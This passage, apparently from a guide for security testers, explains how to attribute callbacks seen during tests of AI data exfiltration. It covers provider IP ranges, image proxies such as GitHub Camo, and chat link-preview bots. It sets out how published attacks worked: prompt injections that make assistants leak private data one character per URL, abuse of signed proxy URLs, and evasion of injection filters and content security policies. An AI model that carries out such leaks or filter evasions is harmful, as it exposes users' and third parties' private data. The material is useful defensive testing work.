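Address       172.170.1.82    last number in binary: 0101 0010
Range end     172.170.1.95    last number in binary: 0101 1111
Next address  172.170.1.96    last number in binary: 0110 0000
```

The address 172.170.1.82 begins with the same four bits as the start of the range, so it matches. The address 172.170.1.96 does not. Most programming languages have a library for this. In Python the test is one line:

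```
ip_address("172.170.1.82") in ip_network("172.170.1.80/28")   # True
```

Searching the file for a range as text is less reliable, because an operator can write the same addresses in more than one way. One range in the thread, 51.59.24.64/27, covers 32 addresses. OpenAI's file listed them as two neighbouring /28 ranges, so a text search for the /27 would have found nothing.

The result also depends on the date of the file. OpenAI added this range in its 8 July 2026 refresh, so a callback from 172.170.1.82 on 1 July would have matched nothing if checked that day, but would have pointed to OpenAI if checked two weeks later.

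The file in force on the day of a callback is the best record of which addresses OpenAI claimed at the time. A newer file can give the wrong answer because cloud companies reassign addresses. If OpenAI has since given up a range and removed it from the file, a request that OpenAI did make will have no match. If OpenAI has since taken over a range that another customer used on the day of the test, that customer's request will produce a false match. Testers need to keep a copy of the file because each new version replaces the old one at the same web address. Each file has a `creationTime` field that identifies the version.

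In the same thread, OpenAI described its ranges as "best effort" and recommended mutual TLS, in which both the client and the server present certificates. OpenAI documents this for plugins, so testers can use it when they run a service that ChatGPT connects to. They shouldn't expect a certificate from a service that only opens a planted page.

Even a correct address match identifies only OpenAI's network, not the mailbox that leaked. A tester who plants URLs in ten mailboxes can find out which one leaked by putting a different identifier in each URL.

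### What other providers publish

Anthropic, Google, Microsoft and Perplexity publish different amounts of information about their fetchers. In the Perplexity row, the names come from Cloudflare and the address file comes from Cloudflare's bot directory.

| Provider | Fetcher acting for a user | Crawler | How to check an address | Date checked |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| OpenAI | ChatGPT-User | GPTBot, OAI-SearchBot, OAI-AdsBot | A separate file for each | 25 July 2026 (web fetchers), 24 August 2026 (other services) |
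| Anthropic | Claude-User, and Claude-Agent for hosted browsers | ClaudeBot, Claude-SearchBot | One list for its robots, with separate documentation for Claude-Agent | 20 November 2026 |
| Google | Google-Agent, Google-GeminiNotebook | Googlebot | Three files for user-triggered fetchers, and reverse DNS | 19 November 2026 |
| Microsoft | No published Copilot identity found | Bingbot | A Bingbot file and a lookup tool | December 2026 |
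| Perplexity | Perplexity-User | PerplexityBot | `perplexity-user.json` for Perplexity-User | December 2026 |

Anthropic's ranges are in other companies' clouds, so site owners sometimes look up a ClaudeBot address, see Google Cloud and wrongly conclude that the request is fake, as TrustMyIP describes. A tester should check the address against Anthropic's list first. Testers can also make the opposite mistake and attribute a request to the provider's servers when it came from a developer's own machine, because some command-line tools send a provider's user agent.

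Google's list separates agents from other fetchers that act for a user. Google says Google-Agent is for agents that run on its infrastructure and browse at a user's request, and its addresses are in `user-triggered-agents.json`. The fetcher for Gemini Notebook (formerly NotebookLM) requests pages that users add as sources. For user-triggered fetchers that Google itself owns, a reverse DNS lookup returns a name that begins with `google-proxy-` and ends in `google.com`. The list has no separate entry for the Gemini chat app, but Google says the list is incomplete.

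Microsoft's Copilot may never contact the listener during a conversation. Microsoft says Copilot writes a short query based on the user's prompt and sends it to Bing, and PPC Land notes that Copilot's answers draw on the index that Bingbot builds. So the only callback might come from Bingbot, days before anyone asks Copilot about the page. Search Engine Land's *Microsoft list of Bingbot IP addresses released* describes the address file and lookup tool for checking whether a request came from Bingbot. Cloudflare's *Microsoft Preview* describes another Microsoft fetcher, MicrosoftPreview, which makes snapshots of pages for Microsoft products. Some bot directories list user agents for Copilot without tracing them to any Microsoft page.

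The providers also differ in whether they obey `robots.txt`, the file that lists what automated visitors may fetch from a website. Anthropic says its robots, including Claude-User, obey it. Google's user-triggered fetchers generally ignore it, and OpenAI says `robots.txt` rules may not apply to ChatGPT-User. If a listener's `robots.txt` forbids everything, a tester could get a callback from ChatGPT and none from Claude even though both models tried to open the URL. Removing the restriction before the test avoids this.

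### ZombieAgent and the public index

After ShadowLeak, OpenAI stopped ChatGPT from adding anything to a URL it had been given. Radware's *ZombieAgent* shows how to get around that restriction without changing any URLs. The outsider supplies a fixed URL for each letter and digit, and the model spells out the data by opening the matching URLs in order.

Requests can arrive out of order, so Radware also made separate URLs for each position in the text. For a block of ten characters, this takes 26 × 10 URLs for the letters and 10 × 10 for the digits, or 360 in all. A separate URL stands for a space. Each request carries only one character, so someone has to put the requests in order to read the data. Searching the log for a marker in plain text or Base64 would find nothing.

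In the main version of ZombieAgent, OpenAI's servers opened the URLs. Radware also tested a less reliable version in which the model wrote the URLs as images and the user's browser loaded them. The paths in the log could look the same in both cases, but the browser version would also reveal the user's IP address.

The trigger could also vary. In one version, the user shared a file that made ChatGPT save new instructions in its memory, the store of facts it keeps between conversations. ChatGPT then read the outsider's email and leaked data before answering each message, even in a new chat. A tester who looked only at the conversation open when a callback arrived might find nothing suspicious.

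Radware reported ZombieAgent on 26 September 2025. Bugcrowd reproduced it four days later, and OpenAI fixed it on 16 December. Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data* (2026) dates the public report to 8 January. OpenAI described a stricter rule on 28 January. ZombieAgent came after ShadowLeak but before OpenAI described the rule, so it does not show that the rule failed.

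The rule relies on an index of public URLs, which OpenAI's crawler builds without access to users' conversations or accounts. Before an agent loads a URL automatically, OpenAI checks whether that exact URL is in the index. If it is, the agent can load it. Otherwise, OpenAI either tells the agent to try a different website or warns the user that the link may contain information from the conversation.

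OpenAI reasons that a URL the crawler found independently is much less likely to contain a particular user's private data. For example, the index might contain `listener.example/i.png`, but it should not contain `listener.example/i.png?d=blue-heron` if a model has only just added the marker. OpenAI considered trusting whole websites instead, but many well-known sites can redirect visitors elsewhere. A strict list of sites would also produce frequent warnings, and people might learn to click through them.

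The index makes ZombieAgent harder, because an outsider's newly created URLs would fail the check, but it does not rule out the method. Embrace The Red points out that someone with a large website may already have 36 indexed URLs, enough for one per letter and digit. The model's choice of which URL to fetch can then reveal private data, even though the URLs themselves contain none. One choice from 36 URLs conveys log₂ 36, or about 5.2 bits. One choice from 4,096 conveys 12 bits, enough to pick one word from a vocabulary of that size.

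Rehberger suggests that OpenAI could cache pages for a few minutes or stop an agent from opening the same URL twice in a session. Either measure would interfere with spelling a word that repeats a letter. They would do less against Radware's numbered URLs, which use a different URL for each position of a letter. However, the numbered URLs would require the outsider to get many more pages into the index.

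Rehberger also worries that some OpenAI developers might not use the check in their products. He dates OpenAI's additional URL checks to around August 2025, yet ZombieAgent still worked in late September, which is some reason for concern. The checks may not yet have covered the route Radware used, or they may have been weaker then.

Willison reported that OpenAI has also released Lockdown Mode, an account setting that limits outgoing requests that could leak data. Testers should record whether it is on, since it could prevent a callback that the same test would produce on an account without it.

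Other providers have also had to restrict their fetchers. In July 2026, Willison described a leak through Claude's `web_fetch` tool that revealed a user's name, home city and employer. In response, Anthropic removed the tool's ability to follow links in pages it had fetched. A tester who plants a page that links to a second planted page may therefore get one callback from Claude instead of the expected two.

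### Which callbacks a tester now sees

The index rule makes a missing callback harder to interpret. A model may follow the planted instructions and try to open a URL containing private data, but the rule blocks the request before it reaches the listener. A tester needs the conversation or a record of the tool calls to distinguish this case from one in which the model ignored the instructions.

The callbacks that do arrive depend on how the URL got into the test:

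| How the URL enters the test | Expected result at the listener |
|---|---|
| The model makes a new URL containing the marker | No automatic request. If the user accepts the warning, their browser may open the link |
| The user types the URL into the chat | A request from OpenAI's servers, probably as ChatGPT-User |
| The URL is on a public page that OpenAI's crawler has found | A crawler's request first, then possibly one from ChatGPT-User |
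| The model chooses from a set of indexed URLs | Several requests, none containing the marker |

The second row can mislead a tester who wants a quick result. As Rehberger understands it, ChatGPT treats a URL in the user's own message as safe for that session. Typing the planted URL into the chat may therefore produce a callback, but that callback doesn't show that an outsider could have caused one. Typing in a fresh URL with no private data is still a useful control, because the resulting entry shows what address range and headers to expect from the fetcher that day.

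When a user accepts a warning, the link may open in the user's browser, so the fetch comes from the browser rather than the provider. In that case, the listener receives the user's address and the headers that a browser sends for a click, as described for the log viewer. Before OpenAI introduced the rule, the provider could have fetched the same URL.

Requests from the indexing crawler are a separate case because they can happen without any conversation. OpenAI does not name the crawler behind its index, but OAI-SearchBot is the most likely one, and GPTBot's crawls can also be used for search. If either requests a planted URL, the request shows at most that OpenAI's crawler found the URL. No user's data has leaked unless the URL already contained some.

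A crawler's visit can still affect a later test. Once the URL is in the index, ChatGPT may load it automatically, so a test that produced no callback on Monday might produce one on Friday with the same model and planted text. Testers should use a new URL for each run and keep it off public pages unless they want to test the index. They should also expect crawlers after a successful fetch. Willison saw a request from Bingbot just over a minute after one from ChatGPT agent.

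### Who is exposed

In a case like ShadowLeak, the listener's owner receives data from the user's mailbox but not the user's IP address or device details. The time of the request shows roughly when the user ran the task. The data may also concern someone other than the user. In Radware's example, it belonged to an employee named in a personnel email, who might never have used ChatGPT. One version of ZombieAgent collected the email addresses of the user's correspondents from an inbox, and the outsider's server could then send them the same attack.

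The request to the outside server goes from OpenAI's cloud to the listener without crossing the office network, so the employer's network logs contain no record of it. A web gateway, monitoring software on the user's computer and a browser's content security policy all miss it for the same reason. Radware sells protection for AI agents and has an interest in stressing this gap, but the gap follows directly from the request's route.

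The employer may still have indirect evidence. Its network logs could show that the user connected to ChatGPT, and the mail provider's records could show that a connector read the mailbox. Neither would show where the agent sent the data. To find that out, an investigator would need OpenAI's records, the agent's activity log or the log of the server that received the request.

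## An image proxy: CamoLeak and GitHub Camo

A callback from a company's servers can look like a browsing tool's request even when a person's browser triggered it. This happens when the page that displays a model's answer loads its images through an image proxy.

GitHub runs such a proxy, called Camo. At first Camo handled only images from sites without HTTPS, because browsers warn about insecure images on a secure page. In January 2014 GitHub extended it to HTTPS images. GitHub's announcement, *Proxying User Images* (2014), gives privacy as one reason, since other companies would no longer receive visitors' browser details. GitHub also expected images to load faster through its CDN.

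### How Camo fetches an image

Suppose a developer adds a picture from `listener.example` to a README, the introductory page of a code repository. According to Legit Security's *CamoLeak*, the process works as follows:

1. GitHub's software searches the text for images on hosts outside GitHub.
2. It signs each image's address with a secret key. It then replaces the address with a new one at `camo.githubusercontent.com`, which contains both the signature and the original address.
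3. A visitor opens the README, and the visitor's browser requests the picture from Camo.
4. Camo checks the signature. If it is valid, Camo downloads the picture from `listener.example` and passes it to the browser.

The listener records the callback in step 4, but the trigger is the display of the page in step 3.

The signature is an HMAC (hash-based message authentication code), a short code that a program computes from a message and a secret key. Here the message is the full address of the image:

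```
signature = HMAC(secret key, "https://listener.example/k7q2.png")
```

Someone without the key cannot feasibly compute the right signature for a new URL. The signature is 40 hexadecimal digits long, according to the README of *camo*, GitHub's published code for the proxy. That is 160 bits, so a random guess has one chance in 2¹⁶⁰ of being right. If a model adds `?d=blue-heron` to the image's address, the old signature no longer matches and Camo refuses the request. The browser can't bypass Camo either, because GitHub's content security policy blocks images from outside hosts.

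A Camo address in the format that GitHub uses looks like this:

```
https://camo.githubusercontent.com/<40-digit signature>/
68747470733a2f2f6c697374656e65722e6578616d706c652f6b3771322e706e67
```

The long number is the original address with each character written as two hexadecimal digits, so `68` stands for "h" and `74` for "t". The address isn't encrypted, so a defender who finds a Camo address in a browser's history can decode it without GitHub's key and learn which outside host the image came from.

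### What the image's host receives

The listener's entry for this picture would look roughly like this (an invented example):

```
192.0.2.61   10:31:02 UTC   GET /k7q2.png
User-Agent: github-camo ...
Via: github-camo ...
```

In *I leant something new trying to build a Github profile analytics tool*, EDDYMENS describes putting an invisible image in a GitHub profile to learn visitors' locations and devices. The server log instead contained the user agent `github-camo` and an address belonging to GitHub.

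In the published code, one setting supplies the text for both the user agent and the Via header. The default is "Camo Asset Proxy" with a version number, so `github-camo` reflects GitHub's configuration and could change. A request is suspicious if the two headers don't match, although a forger could copy both. The source address is better evidence. However, according to an old version of the README, GitHub ran Camo on Heroku, a hosting company, so requests from that period could have come from addresses not registered to GitHub.

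The host does not receive the viewer's address or user agent. Anton Komarev, who runs a popular view counter for GitHub profiles, explains in *github profile views counter* that his server can only add one for each request from the proxy because "we don't know who initiated it".

GitHub warns that anyone who obtains a Camo address can use it to view the image. A script could therefore trigger a callback that looks the same as one triggered by a reader's browser.

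### CamoLeak

Omer Mayraz of Legit Security found a way to leak private data through Camo in June 2025, as SecurityWeek's *GitHub Copilot Chat Flaw Leaked Data From Private Repositories* reports. His target was GitHub Copilot Chat, an assistant that answers questions about code. It works with the permissions of the person asking, so it can read that person's private repositories. In outline, the attack went as follows:

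1. The outsider sets up a web server with a separate image address for each letter and symbol. Every address returns the same transparent picture, one pixel wide.
2. The outsider obtains a valid Camo address for each one. GitHub's programming interface converts any Markdown that a user submits, including the image addresses in it.
3. The outsider opens a pull request (a proposed change to a repository) and hides a prompt injection in its description, using GitHub's own feature for invisible comments. The hidden text includes the list of Camo addresses.
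4. Another user opens the pull request and asks Copilot Chat to explain it. Copilot reads the hidden comment too, and looks up something in the user's private repositories.
5. Copilot writes what it found as a row of images, with one image for each character.
6. The user's browser displays the answer and requests the images from Camo. All the signatures are valid, so Camo fetches the images from the outsider's server, and the outsider reads the text from the order of the requests.

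In Legit Security's demonstration, the leaked text described an undisclosed vulnerability in a private project. Copilot also searched a user's whole codebase for Amazon cloud keys and leaked the result. If the private text were the marker "blue-heron", the listener's log would begin like this (again invented):

```
10:31:02.114   GET /b.png   User-Agent: github-camo ...
10:31:02.120   GET /l.png   User-Agent: github-camo ...
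10:31:02.131   GET /u.png   User-Agent: github-camo ...
10:31:02.139   GET /e.png   User-Agent: github-camo ...
```

The HMAC worked as designed. A valid signature shows that GitHub signed the address at some point, but it doesn't tie the address to a particular page or person, so addresses that GitHub had signed for the attacker also worked in another user's chat. OpenAI's index of public URLs has the same limitation.

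Legit Security relied on the images loading in order, but the proxy, like the viewer's computer, can change the order of requests. Radware's solution in ZombieAgent, a separate address for each character at each position in the text, would be awkward here because GitHub would have to sign every address. With 95 printable characters and 100 positions, the hidden comment would need 9,500 signed addresses.

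Anyone who asked Copilot about the pull request could trigger the attack. If two people did so at once, as might happen on a busy pull request, their letters would arrive mixed together. The source addresses would not help separate them because all the requests come from Camo.

### Why the remedy was in the chat page

The log entries from CamoLeak resemble those from a provider's browsing tool. In both, the requests come from a company's servers and the user agent names an automated client. A tester who relied only on these details might report that Copilot had opened URLs on the outsider's server and recommend restricting its web access.

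That recommendation would have missed the cause. Copilot only wrote text, and the leak began when the chat page turned that text into images. Removing every browsing tool would not have stopped the attack, but displaying the answer as plain text would have. According to Legit Security, GitHub disabled images in Copilot Chat completely and reported the flaw fixed as of 14 August 2025. Petri's *GitHub Copilot Chat Hit by ‘CamoLeak’ Flaw Allowing Silent Data Exfiltration* adds that GitHub also blocked this use of Camo.

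Testers who suspect a proxy can check for it in a few ways:

- Watch the network panel in the browser's developer tools while the answer appears. If the display is the trigger, the panel will show requests to the proxy's host.
- Request the same answer through an interface that shows only plain text. The callbacks should stop.
- Close the chat page and open the saved conversation later. New callbacks at that moment point to the display, because the model is not running.

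Timing alone cannot show that a callback in the middle of an answer came from a tool call. Chat pages usually display an answer while the model is still writing it, so the browser can request an image well before the answer is complete.

### What proxy caching hides

An image proxy can cache each image it downloads and serve the copy to later viewers, so the image's host gets no request for those views. The blog post *How to track and display profile views on GitHub* says that Camo will cache an image after the first request unless the image's host sends headers to prevent it.

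Caching can garble a message like the one in CamoLeak. "Blue-heron" has ten characters, but the "e" appears twice. If a cache supplies the second "e", the listener receives nine requests and the tester reads "blue-hron". If the tester soon ran a second test with the marker "blue-robin", while those nine images were still in the cache, the listener would receive just one callback, for the letter "i".

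Mayraz avoided this by having Copilot append a new random number to each Camo address. The signature covers only the original image's address, so the extra number did not invalidate it. The number presumably made each request look new to the caches between the viewer and Camo. Because it was not part of the original image's address, Camo would not have passed it on, so it is unlikely to appear in the listener's log.

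With caching, the proxy makes a callback only when it needs a fresh copy of the image, so there may be far fewer callbacks than views. The callback times can also mislead. One callback on Monday could mean one viewer that day, or that viewer and twenty more later in the week. If a tester previews a planted image on Monday and the intended reader sees it on Tuesday, the only callback may come from the preview.

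GitHub recommends that hosts send `Cache-Control: no-cache` with images that change. Despite its name, this header lets a cache keep a copy, but requires it to check with the host before reusing it. Those checks appear in the listener's log as more callbacks. People can also remove an image from Camo's cache with a command, but GitHub asks them to do this sparingly because it affects every GitHub user who views the image. For a test, using a new image URL is simpler.

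Camo also limits file size and accepts only certain image types. These limits do not prevent a callback, because Camo has to contact the host before it can learn the file's type. The listener may therefore have received a request even if the image appears broken on the page.

### EchoLeak: a request through Teams

GitHub built Camo to fetch images for viewers. In two attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that can search a user's work email and files, outsiders found other Microsoft services that could also fetch images for viewers.

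*Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) describes the first of these attacks, which researchers at the security company Aim Security found. An outsider sends an employee an email containing a prompt injection worded as advice to the employee, so Microsoft's filter does not recognise it as an instruction to an AI system. The email is long and covers many office topics, which makes Copilot more likely to retrieve it. When the employee later asks Copilot about one of those topics, Copilot's answer includes an image whose URL contains private data.

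Copilot's filter removed ordinary Markdown images with outside addresses, but it missed a less common notation that puts the address on a separate line. The Copilot page's content security policy still blocked images from any host not on an approved list. Aim Security searched the approved hosts for a service that would fetch another address on request. It found one in SharePoint, but the victim would first have had to accept an invitation to the attacker's site. A Microsoft Teams service also fetched addresses on request and required no invitation.

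Published accounts differ on where the request in the outsider's log would have come from. Reddy and Gujral (2025) write in *EchoLeak* that it would come either from Microsoft's servers or from the victim's own address. Ravia says that the SharePoint server makes the request on the client's behalf and that the Teams URL has the same result, but he prints no log.

Ravia's version is more convincing because the policy barred the browser from contacting the outsider's server. Even if Teams had redirected the browser there, the policy would have blocked the image. So the last request almost certainly came from the Teams service. The outsider could have received the victim's address only if that service had copied it into a header, which neither account reports.

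The callback occurred only after the employee asked a question that led Copilot to retrieve the email, so an email sent on Monday might cause no callback until Thursday. Aim Security reported the flaw in January 2025. According to Reddy and Gujral, Microsoft fixed it on its servers in May and published an advisory on 11 June.

### SearchLeak: a request through Bing

Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes a similar leak from the search page of Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise. This one required the user to click a link to a genuine Microsoft page. Copilot treated the search text in the link as instructions, searched the user's mailbox, and output an image whose URL contained the title of an email.

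Microsoft had a safeguard that turned such images into harmless text, but it ran only after Copilot had finished its answer. Before then, the browser displayed the unfinished answer and requested the image. The policy allowed requests to Bing, whose image search accepts an image URL and downloads the image for analysis. Varonis states that Bing's infrastructure makes this download, not the victim's browser. The outsider's log contained the email's title in plain words, with underscores for spaces.

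The list of approved hosts that Ravia printed in 2025 already included Bing, so the route SearchLeak used was probably open while Microsoft was fixing EchoLeak. The Next Web reports that Microsoft assigned the SearchLeak flaw the identifier CVE-2026-42824 on 4 June 2026 and rated it critical. Microsoft had patched it by 15 June, when Varonis published its findings.

| | CamoLeak | EchoLeak | SearchLeak |
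|---|---|---|---|
| What the user does | Asks Copilot Chat about a pull request | Asks Copilot a work question | Clicks a link to Copilot's search page |
| Trigger | The browser displays the answer | The browser displays the answer | The browser displays the unfinished answer |
| Where the browser sends its request | GitHub Camo | A Teams service | Bing image search |
| Fetcher | GitHub Camo | The Teams service | Bing's servers |
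| Data in each request | One character | Text that Copilot chose as sensitive | The title of an email |

A tester could easily dismiss a SearchLeak callback as a search engine's routine visit. Microsoft's list of Bingbot addresses may not show whether it was one, because the image search service could use different addresses from the crawler. Anyone can ask Bing to analyse a picture, so the best evidence is a marker that exists only in the test mailbox. Only someone or something with access to the mailbox could put that marker in the picture's address.

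The browser sends the first request from the user's computer across the office network to Bing, Teams or Camo, which gives an employer evidence that it would not have in a case like ShadowLeak. trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* recommends that defenders decode any address inside a request to a trusted service. With SearchLeak, this would have revealed the outsider's server and the email's title. Decoding works only if the company's web gateway decrypts traffic and logs full addresses, and the log then also contains the leaked data. A rule that ignores all requests to Microsoft would miss the leak.

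The browser can also report requests that violate a page's content security policy. These reports cover at most the browser's request to Bing, not Bing's request to the outsider.

A tester cannot infer from a product's name whether a proxy is involved. Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* describes a test of Microsoft's Copilot Chat in a development environment, where the software that displayed the answer contacted the outside server directly, so the callback would come from the developer's network rather than GitHub's. Microsoft closed that report in November 2025 without a fix, saying the behavior did not meet its definition of a vulnerability.

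### How other proxies identify themselves

GitHub's user agent is unusually clear. For comparison, the user agent of Gmail's image proxy named Firefox 3.0.7 and ended with `(via ggpht.com)` when Valsorda (2013) tested it for *How the new Gmail image proxy works*. Google had just introduced the proxy, and Valsorda emailed himself a message with an image hosted on his own server. His server received no request when the message arrived on his phone or when he opened his inbox on a computer. It received one when he opened the message, just over two minutes after sending it.

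Taken literally, the full user agent describes a German-language copy of a 2009 browser on Windows XP. Valsorda normally used Chrome on a Mac, in English and Italian. The only useful clue in the user agent is its ending, which includes the Google domain `ggpht.com`. The source address's host name began with `google-proxy-`, which also pointed to Google.

If a tester plants a URL in a Gmail mailbox and the email contains an image, a person who opens the email can cause a callback through this proxy before any AI system has read it. Google now uses the `google-proxy-` prefix for other fetchers that act for users, so the host name alone may not be enough to tell Gmail from one of Google's AI products. Using a plain link and no image in the email avoids the problem.

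Gmail's proxy did not cache the picture in Valsorda's test, so his server received another request each time he downloaded it. A sender could therefore still learn when and how often the recipient opened a message. His article is old and Google may have changed the system since, so anyone relying on these details should repeat the test.

The email service HEY documents its image proxy much better. The proxy's user agent begins with `hey.com/imageproxy`, followed by an ordinary description of Chrome on Linux, and its client hints contain the same name. HEY says that requests come from `gopher.hey.com` and suggests checking this with a reverse DNS lookup, which needs to be confirmed with a forward lookup, as with Google's crawlers. HEY warns that its addresses can change, so an old list of them is of little use.

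HEY's proxy sends US English as the language preference for every user and sends no Referer. It caches images but respects the host's caching instructions. HEY says this prevents senders from tracking when users view their email. This holds for later views served from the cache, but an image with a unique URL would still produce a callback the first time a user opened the message.

### When a proxy passes on the viewer's details

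Other organisations run their own proxies, often with go-camo, an independent program that works like GitHub's Camo. GitLab, a rival code-hosting platform, recommends go-camo to customers who run GitLab on their own servers. The source address of a request from an organisation's own proxy may identify the viewer's employer but does not identify the viewer.

Go-camo also forwards some of the browser's headers to the image's host, according to the documentation for version 2.6.3, pkg.go.dev's *camo* (2025). They include Accept, which can be a clue to the type of browser, and Accept-Language, so a language preference in the callback may be the viewer's own. HEY's proxy sets Accept-Language itself, so the header gives no information about the viewer there.

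A more serious problem is that the proxy may forward the viewer's address. An older version of go-camo, also documented on pkg.go.dev, passed on the X-Forwarded-For header by default. According to its changelog, a later release turned this off and added an option, `--enable-xfwd4`, to turn it back on. A tester who knows only that a company uses go-camo can't tell whether its proxy forwards the address.

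Even with the option on, what the image's host receives depends on how the company has arranged its servers. The README describes the option as "passthrough/generation", meaning that go-camo can pass on a header it has received or create one. The README also recommends placing a CDN in front of the proxy. Go-camo's incoming connection then comes from the CDN, so a header created from that connection would contain only the CDN's address. If the CDN had already recorded the viewer's address in the header, go-camo could pass it on to the image's host.

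It is easier to test whether the proxy exposes a viewer's address than to work it out. The tester displays a planted image from a connection with a known public address, then searches for that address in the full headers of the request the listener receives. If the address appears anywhere in them, the proxy has exposed it.

### Who is exposed

With GitHub Camo, the outsider gets data from the viewer's account, but the viewer's IP address stays hidden. In CamoLeak, the viewer might be one developer with access to a company's private code, so the leak would expose the whole company. If the leaked text contains a working cloud key, replacing the key is more urgent than finding out whose browser displayed the answer.

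Camo's callback doesn't identify that person, so GitHub's records are the best place to look for them. The time of the callback can narrow the search if caching has not interfered. The company can also check its web gateway's log for a burst of requests to `camo.githubusercontent.com` and decode the requested URLs.

The proxy hides the viewer only when their browser goes through it. Before Mayraz turned to images, he had Copilot write an ordinary link with private data in its URL. Clicking that link would have sent the data directly to the outsider's server and revealed the user's IP address. Legit Security mentions only images when describing GitHub's fix, so anyone retesting Copilot Chat should also try a link.

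## A chat platform's preview bot: OpenClaw on Telegram and Slack

GitHub's Camo fetches an image when a browser displays a page. A chat platform may fetch a URL earlier, as soon as someone posts a message containing it, to build a link preview. When an AI agent writes the message, private data in the URL can reach an outside server before anyone reads the message.

PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* described this problem in February 2026. Its main example was OpenClaw, an open-source AI agent that people run on their own machines and talk to through chat apps. During a task, the agent reads material containing a prompt injection and follows it, adding private data to a URL on an attacker's domain and including that URL in its reply. If the chat is on Telegram, Telegram's preview bot then requests the full URL. PromptArmor found that OpenClaw's default Telegram settings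 allowed this.

Telegram's bot fetches the URL when the message is posted. OpenClaw never contacts the outsider's server, which limits what network defences around the agent can do. The Hacker News (2026) reports that China's national computer emergency team, CNCERT, criticised OpenClaw's weak default security. The advice to users included strengthening network controls and running the agent in a container, which isolates it from the rest of the machine. Those measures may reduce other risks, but an agent in a container can still send the message if the container can reach Telegram.

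The chat history is useful evidence because the URL stays in the conversation unless someone deletes it. An investigator can search for the outsider's domain to find when the agent posted the link and who could read it. The link may look harmless, so it is best to examine the message's raw text. Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* warns that an attacker can have the data written in invisible characters.

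OpenClaw's *gateway*, the process that connects the agent to chat applications, sends each reply to the application the user's message came from. According to OpenClaw, the model does not choose the application. So if an ordinary reply caused a callback from Telegram's bot, the conversation was probably on Telegram.

### The public test site

PromptArmor set up a public site, AITextRisk, where people could test their own combinations of agent and chat application. The site showed whether an agent's link had triggered a preview request and what data the request contained. One example entry includes a name and an API key.

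The site also counted the preview bots it saw most often, such as Slack's and Telegram's. A preview bot's request can identify the chat application but not the agent that wrote the link, so PromptArmor let visitors "claim" a log entry and report which agent was responsible. Visitors could also report agents whose links had produced no preview.

Apostol's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* describes the resulting charts. The risky combinations included Microsoft Teams with Copilot Studio (Microsoft's tool for building agents) and Slack with certain bots. Apostol also lists Discord, Telegram and Apple among the affected platforms. PromptArmor's article gives the most detail about OpenClaw on Telegram, including a setting that stops the leak.

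The site's logs are good evidence that chat platforms request links like these. The reported combinations are weaker evidence because visitors supplied them. A visitor could name the wrong agent, or paste the link into the chat by hand, and the request would look the same. The charts also can't show how common the problem is. People who visit a security test site are not a random sample of users, and a popular application would collect more entries even if it were no riskier than the others.

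Reports that a combination is safe need even more care. The agent may have refused to write the link, an administrator may have turned previews off, or the platform may have reused an earlier response. Slack says it caches responses to preview requests across its service for around 30 minutes. If two visitors' agents wrote the same URL within that time, the second visitor might see no request and report the agent as safe.

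### Where the preview is made

In PromptArmor's OpenClaw example, the platform's servers generate the preview, but some applications generate previews on the sender's or recipient's device. Where the preview is generated affects almost everything in the listener's log.

| | Platform's servers | Sender's device | Recipient's device |
|---|---|---|---|
| Documented example | Slack | WhatsApp (2019 test) | Reddit chat (2020 test) |
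| Usual trigger | Someone posts the message | The sender types or pastes the link | The message appears on the recipient's screen |
| Source address | The platform or its cloud host | The sender's network | The recipient's network |
| Number of callbacks | One or a few, however many people read the message | One or more, sometimes before the sender posts anything | Potentially one or more for each recipient |
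| Whose address leaks | Nobody's | The sender's | Each recipient's |

In all three cases, the listener also receives any data in the URL.

Slack's *Unfurling links in messages* says that its servers have to fetch every URL in a message to find out what kind of content it leads to. Bellingcat's *How To Blow Your Online Cover With URL Previews* (2019) instead reports that Slack's preview request came from the tester's own office address. Slack's account is more convincing because Slack shares a cache across the whole service, which implies that its servers make the requests. Testers can check their own setup by posting a harmless link and seeing which address the request comes from.

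**Sender's device.** In Bellingcat's test, WhatsApp contacted the server from the tester's own public address. It also sent requests continuously while the tester typed the URL, which could leave a trail like this (an invented example):

```
10:40:11   GET /i.png?d=bl            User-Agent: WhatsApp/...
10:40:12   GET /i.png?d=blue-he       User-Agent: WhatsApp/...
10:40:13   GET /i.png?d=blue-heron    User-Agent: WhatsApp/...
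```

A trail of growing URLs suggests that a person was typing, since an agent would normally submit a finished message.

An agent can also be the sender. If it posts through an application on its owner's computer and that application makes the preview, the callback comes from the owner's home or office network. A tester could easily mistake this for the agent opening the URL. The user agent and the application's preview setting can help tell the two apart.

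Signal makes previews on the sender's device but hides the sender's IP address. Signal's *I link therefore I am* explains that the app connects through a proxy and sets up encryption directly with the website. The listener would therefore receive the proxy's IP address and the TLS fingerprint of the sender's app. Signal fetches preview images in overlapping pieces, so one preview can cause several requests. The post describes previews for only four popular sites, so a tester would first need to check that Signal will preview a link to the listener.

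**Recipient's device.** Mysk's *Link Previews* (2020) found that some popular chat apps leaked IP addresses or quietly downloaded gigabytes of data. According to SecurityWeek's report on that research, Reddit's chat made previews on the recipient's device before the recipient tapped the link. Anyone who sent a link to their own server could learn the recipient's IP address and approximate location.

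If an application like this showed an agent's message to five people, the listener could receive five callbacks from five networks, even though the agent had leaked the data only once. The callbacks' IP addresses would belong to the readers, who might have nothing to do with the data in the URL.

These tests are several years old, and the applications may have changed since. Results can also depend on the user's region. Mysk notes that Facebook disabled link previews in Europe in 2021 because of regulations there, so the same test could have given different results inside and outside Europe.

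### How preview bots identify themselves

| Application | Text to look for in the user agent | How to check the source address |
|---|---|---|
| Slack | `Slackbot-LinkExpanding`, `Slack-ImgProxy` or `Slackbot 1.0` | Slack's page about its bots gives no ranges |
| Telegram | `TelegramBot (like TwitterBot)` | Telegram reportedly publishes its bot's addresses |
| Discord | `Discordbot` | An official list, in JSON and plain text |
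| Microsoft Teams | No documented user agent found | No range specific to Teams previews found |
| Apple Messages | `facebookexternalhit/1.1 Facebot Twitterbot/1.0` after a Safari user agent | The sender's own network |

Slack divides the work among three bots. Slackbot-LinkExpanding reads only as much of the page as it needs to find a title and description, and downloads any image, video or audio file that the page's tags point to. Slack-ImgProxy fetches and caches images, much as GitHub's Camo does. Slackbot 1.0 handles other requests, such as calls to services that Slack works with.

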